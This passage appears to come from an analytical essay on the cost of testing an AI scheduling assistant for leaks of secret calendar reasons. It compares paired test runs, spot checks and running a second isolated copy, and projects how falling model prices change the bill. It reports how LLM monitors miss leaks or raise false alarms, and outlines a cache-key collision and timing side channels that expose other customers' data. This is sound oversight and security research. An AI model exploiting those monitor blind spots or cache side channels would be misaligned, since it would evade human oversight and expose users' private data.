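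Token use is unpredictable even when the same model repeats the same task. *TokenCast* (2026) cites up to 30-fold differences between runs of one task, and *How Do AI Agents Spend Your Money?* (2026) found that the most expensive coding tasks also varied the most from run to run. A few dozen trial runs, including some of the hardest requests, would give a tester a usable average before committing to 624,000 runs.

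Time can matter as much as money. The slowest model in *ReproBench* averaged 25 minutes per run. At that speed, 624,000 runs done one after another would take about 30 years, or 11 days with a thousand running at once.

### Why one experiment cost only six dollars

*The Oversight Gap* reports about 26,893 model calls for about $6, or roughly a fiftieth of a cent per call. Judging by that figure alone, paired testing would cost almost nothing.

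But most of those calls asked a model to judge a short exchange at temperature zero. A program wrote the exchanges from templates, and no real agent carried out a task. A *ReproBench* run has 48 calls, most of them with a long history, so $6 would pay for about seven runs, and 26,893 runs would cost about $24,000.

The $6 is a fair guide to the price of judging pairs of short runs, but judging long ones may cost more and be less reliable. When *The Oversight Gap* extended the sessions to 16 turns of invented tool calls and results, average accuracy with both runs and an explicit rule was 86.3%, compared with 90.0% for short exchanges. In sessions of up to 64 turns, five of the seven models held steady or improved, while the other two lost up to 39 percentage points. Comparing the offered slots with a few lines of code would avoid this problem and cost nothing per pair.

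### Tools and alarms

For the 400-run test, labor will probably cost more than running the model. If a programmer spends two weeks building a simulated calendar, mail program and booking service at $100 an hour, $B$ is $8,000. The tester can reuse these tools for every later version of the assistant, which spreads the cost over many tests. A tester who does the 624,000 runs has to repeat them whenever the model changes.

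False alarms cost money. With 200 comparisons and a 5% false-alarm rate, a tester should expect ten false alarms even if nothing leaks. The simplest correction raises the number of runs per calendar to about 4,000 and the total to 1.6 million.

Repeating only the flagged comparisons takes far fewer runs. Repeating ten of them adds 31,200 runs, or 5% of the original total, and leaves an average of 0.5 false alarms. But a real five-point leak now has to show up twice. If each test has an 80% chance of detecting it, the chance of finding it in both is 64%.

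### Ways to lower the bill

Accepting a larger undetected leak saves the most. The table uses the sample sizes calculated earlier and the Sonnet price of $1.03 per run.

| Smallest shift the test should find | Runs for 200 comparisons | Cost |
|---|---|---|
| 50% to 90% | 6,800 | $7,000 |
| 50% to 75% | 22,000 | $23,000 |
| 50% to 60% | 154,000 | $159,000 |
| 50% to 55% | 624,000 | $643,000 |

It makes sense to start at the top of the table because, if the assistant has a large leak, the tester finds it for a few thousand dollars and can fix it before paying for the finer test.

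A narrow projection can make even small leaks practical to detect. If the assistant's choice of slot never varies by chance, the 59 runs per calendar calculated earlier are enough to find a leak that changes the offer in 5% of runs. All 200 comparisons then need 23,600 runs, but the tester learns nothing about leaks through wording or timing.

With ten separate pairs, each request needs runs with 20 calendars. If the tester instead compares ten calendars with one shared reference, each request needs runs with only 11, and the total falls from 624,000 to 343,200.

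Giving the reference more runs than the others lowers the total further, because all ten comparisons use it. The best ratio of reference runs to runs with each of the others is the square root of the number of comparisons, here about 3.2. For the same precision, the tester then needs about 3,250 runs with the reference and 1,030 with each of the others, or roughly 270,000 in all.

Shahriar and colleagues saved runs this way, comparing 7,630 sessions in which the agent held a secret with only 2,130 in which it held none. But an unlucky set of reference runs distorts every comparison that uses it. Two calendars can also differ from each other by more than either differs from the reference. If the assistant offers slot 11 in 50% of runs with the reference, 46% with one calendar and 54% with another, the two calendars are eight points apart, but each is only four points from the reference.

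Stopping early helps most when there is a leak. With the running score described earlier, the assistant that always signals the interview fails after eight pairs of runs. A comparison that finds no leak has to run to its limit, so a tester who expects a clean result should plan for the full number of runs. A test that stops at the first convincing difference also tends to exaggerate the size of the leak, and measuring it accurately takes more runs.

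Replaying the beginning of a run from a saved state avoids paying again for the calls made before the secret enters. If the agent first reads the calendar halfway through its 48 calls, the tester can save the state at that point and start each new run there, which cuts the price on Sonnet by about 43%. The saving is less than half because later calls have longer histories and so cost more. The scheduling assistant reads the calendar almost immediately, so replaying would save very little in its case.

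Runs that share a beginning are also less varied than complete runs. A leak might appear only after a beginning the tester didn't save, so the tester should start runs from several different beginnings.

**Smaller domains** require fewer comparisons. The meeting form described earlier needs only 60 runs if the assistant is deterministic, which costs about $62 on Sonnet. With sampling and a five-point target, it needs 93,600 runs, which cost about $96,000. The drawback of the form is that colleagues can no longer write requests in their own words.

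Some of these savings can be combined. With a stable slot, a single reference calendar and 59 runs per calendar, testing the original 20 requests takes 12,980 runs and costs about $13,000.

### What a shared cache can reveal

The prices above already include caching within each run. Without it, the Sonnet run would cost about $6.70 instead of $1.03. Sharing the cache between runs saves only about five cents more per run, or 5%, if every run begins with the same 20,000 tokens of instructions and tool descriptions. The calendar has to come after this shared text because a cache can reuse a prompt only up to the first difference.

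In a test with invented calendars, the main drawback of reusing a cache is that it can slightly change the model's arithmetic. In production, a shared cache also allows the timing attacks described earlier. The two copies in secure multi-execution have a similar problem if they share a cache, because the user's copy could affect how quickly the public copy responds.

A faulty cache can return the wrong data. Servers store saved work under a short code computed from the beginning of the prompt. If two different prompts produce the same code, one customer's answer may draw on another's data. *The Oversight Gap* demonstrates this with the function a production server uses to compute these codes. A search found two prompts with the same code after 15,261 attempts. Language models that read one of the resulting sessions detected the leak with 51.0% accuracy, about the same as guessing. With a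 second run and a rule for comparing the two, they reached 92.6%.

Keeping a separate cache for each customer and each secrecy level prevents leaks through shared caches. At five cents per run, sharing caches would save a tester little money.

### Testing, spot checks or a second copy

A company can run the comparison on a sample of real requests before it releases an assistant, or it can run two copies of the assistant every time, which makes the comparison unnecessary.

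| | Test before release | Spot checks on 1% of requests | Second copy on every request |
|---|---|---|---|
| Extra runs | 400 to 624,000 per version | One per 100 requests | At most about one per request |
| Delay | The release waits for the test | None if the check happens afterwards | The user's summary waits for the public copy |
| Assurance | A limit on leaks for the tested calendars and requests | A chance of noticing leaks that have already happened | The reasons can't affect what the colleague receives, if the copies are properly separated |

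In a spot check, the system repeats a real request but changes the reason in the calendar and replaces the tools with stand-ins. This covers requests that no tester thought of. If each request costs $1.03, checking 1% of 100,000 requests adds about $1,000.

The chance of catching a rare leak is modest. Suppose the assistant is deterministic, 100 of the 100,000 requests leak, and the replacement reason would expose all of them. The checks catch one leak on average and have a 37% chance of catching none. If the assistant samples its responses, a single pair of runs proves nothing, and the company has to pool many checks to see whether the offers shift. The check records contain real calendars, so they need protection too.

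Having a language model read single logged runs would cost less, but its alarms could be useless. *The Oversight Gap* tested monitors on cases that no single run could settle and let them answer that they could not verify a case. The monitors gave that answer only 12.6% of the time. Llama-3.1-8B approved 98% of the leaks, while Claude Sonnet 4 blocked 81% of the clean sessions, and somebody would have to review every blocked session.

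Running a second copy on each of the 100,000 requests costs up to $103,000. That is more than spot checks cost, but less than a sixth of the price of the 624,000-run test. If an assistant handles fewer than 624,000 requests between versions, running a second copy each time is therefore cheaper than testing for five-point leaks, and it protects every request. The two copies can run at the same time on the provider's servers, and the colleague never has to wait for the user's copy.

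Testing may be the only option for an assistant that needs the hidden reasons to choose a good slot. In that case, I would run the $7,000 test on every version, continue spot checks afterwards, and save the finer test for the few requests where a small leak would do real harm.

### Will falling prices solve the problem?

*AI is getting cheaper faster than any other transformative technology* (Roodman and Bye, 2026), a summary of research at Epoch AI, estimates that the price of reaching a fixed benchmark score has fallen 13-fold a year. At that rate, a year from now the $643,000 test would cost about $49,000.

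The number of runs needed grows with the inverse square of the leak's size, so precision improves more slowly than prices fall. A tester whose budget buys 13 times as many runs can detect leaks only 3.6 times smaller, about 1.4 percentage points instead of 5. Detecting a shift from 50% to 51% takes 25 times as many runs as detecting one from 50% to 55%, and would cost about $16 million today. Prices would have to fall for 15 months before that test cost what the five-point test costs now.

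The price drop could take longer than 15 months. Roodman and Bye find that the price of a given level of performance falls 75-fold a year when the level is new, but only 4.7-fold a year two years later. At the slower rate, the drop would take 25 months. They also caution that benchmarks are an imperfect guide to what AI costs in the market.

A tester may not even see prices fall at the slower rate, because the test has to use the same model as the assistant. If the developer always upgrades to the newest model, that model's price matters more than the price of last year's performance. Fable 5.2 costs only 20% less per token than Fable 5.1. Haiku 5.5 costs 90% less per token than Haiku 4.5 for shorter prompts, but Anthropic puts the average saving at around 75%, and the same text now counts as about 30% more tokens.

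Longer runs also use up the savings from falling prices. *AlphaLab* repeated one research campaign five times, and each repeat used 74 to 97 million input tokens and cost about $50 to $70. At $60 per run, the 400-run test costs $24,000 and the 624,000-run test costs about $37 million. If longer tasks would make an agent's runs 13 times as expensive over a year, a 13-fold fall in prices over that year leaves the bill unchanged. Running a second copy of such an agent would also be expensive, but it would add at most about the cost of one run per task, however small a leak the owner wanted to prevent.
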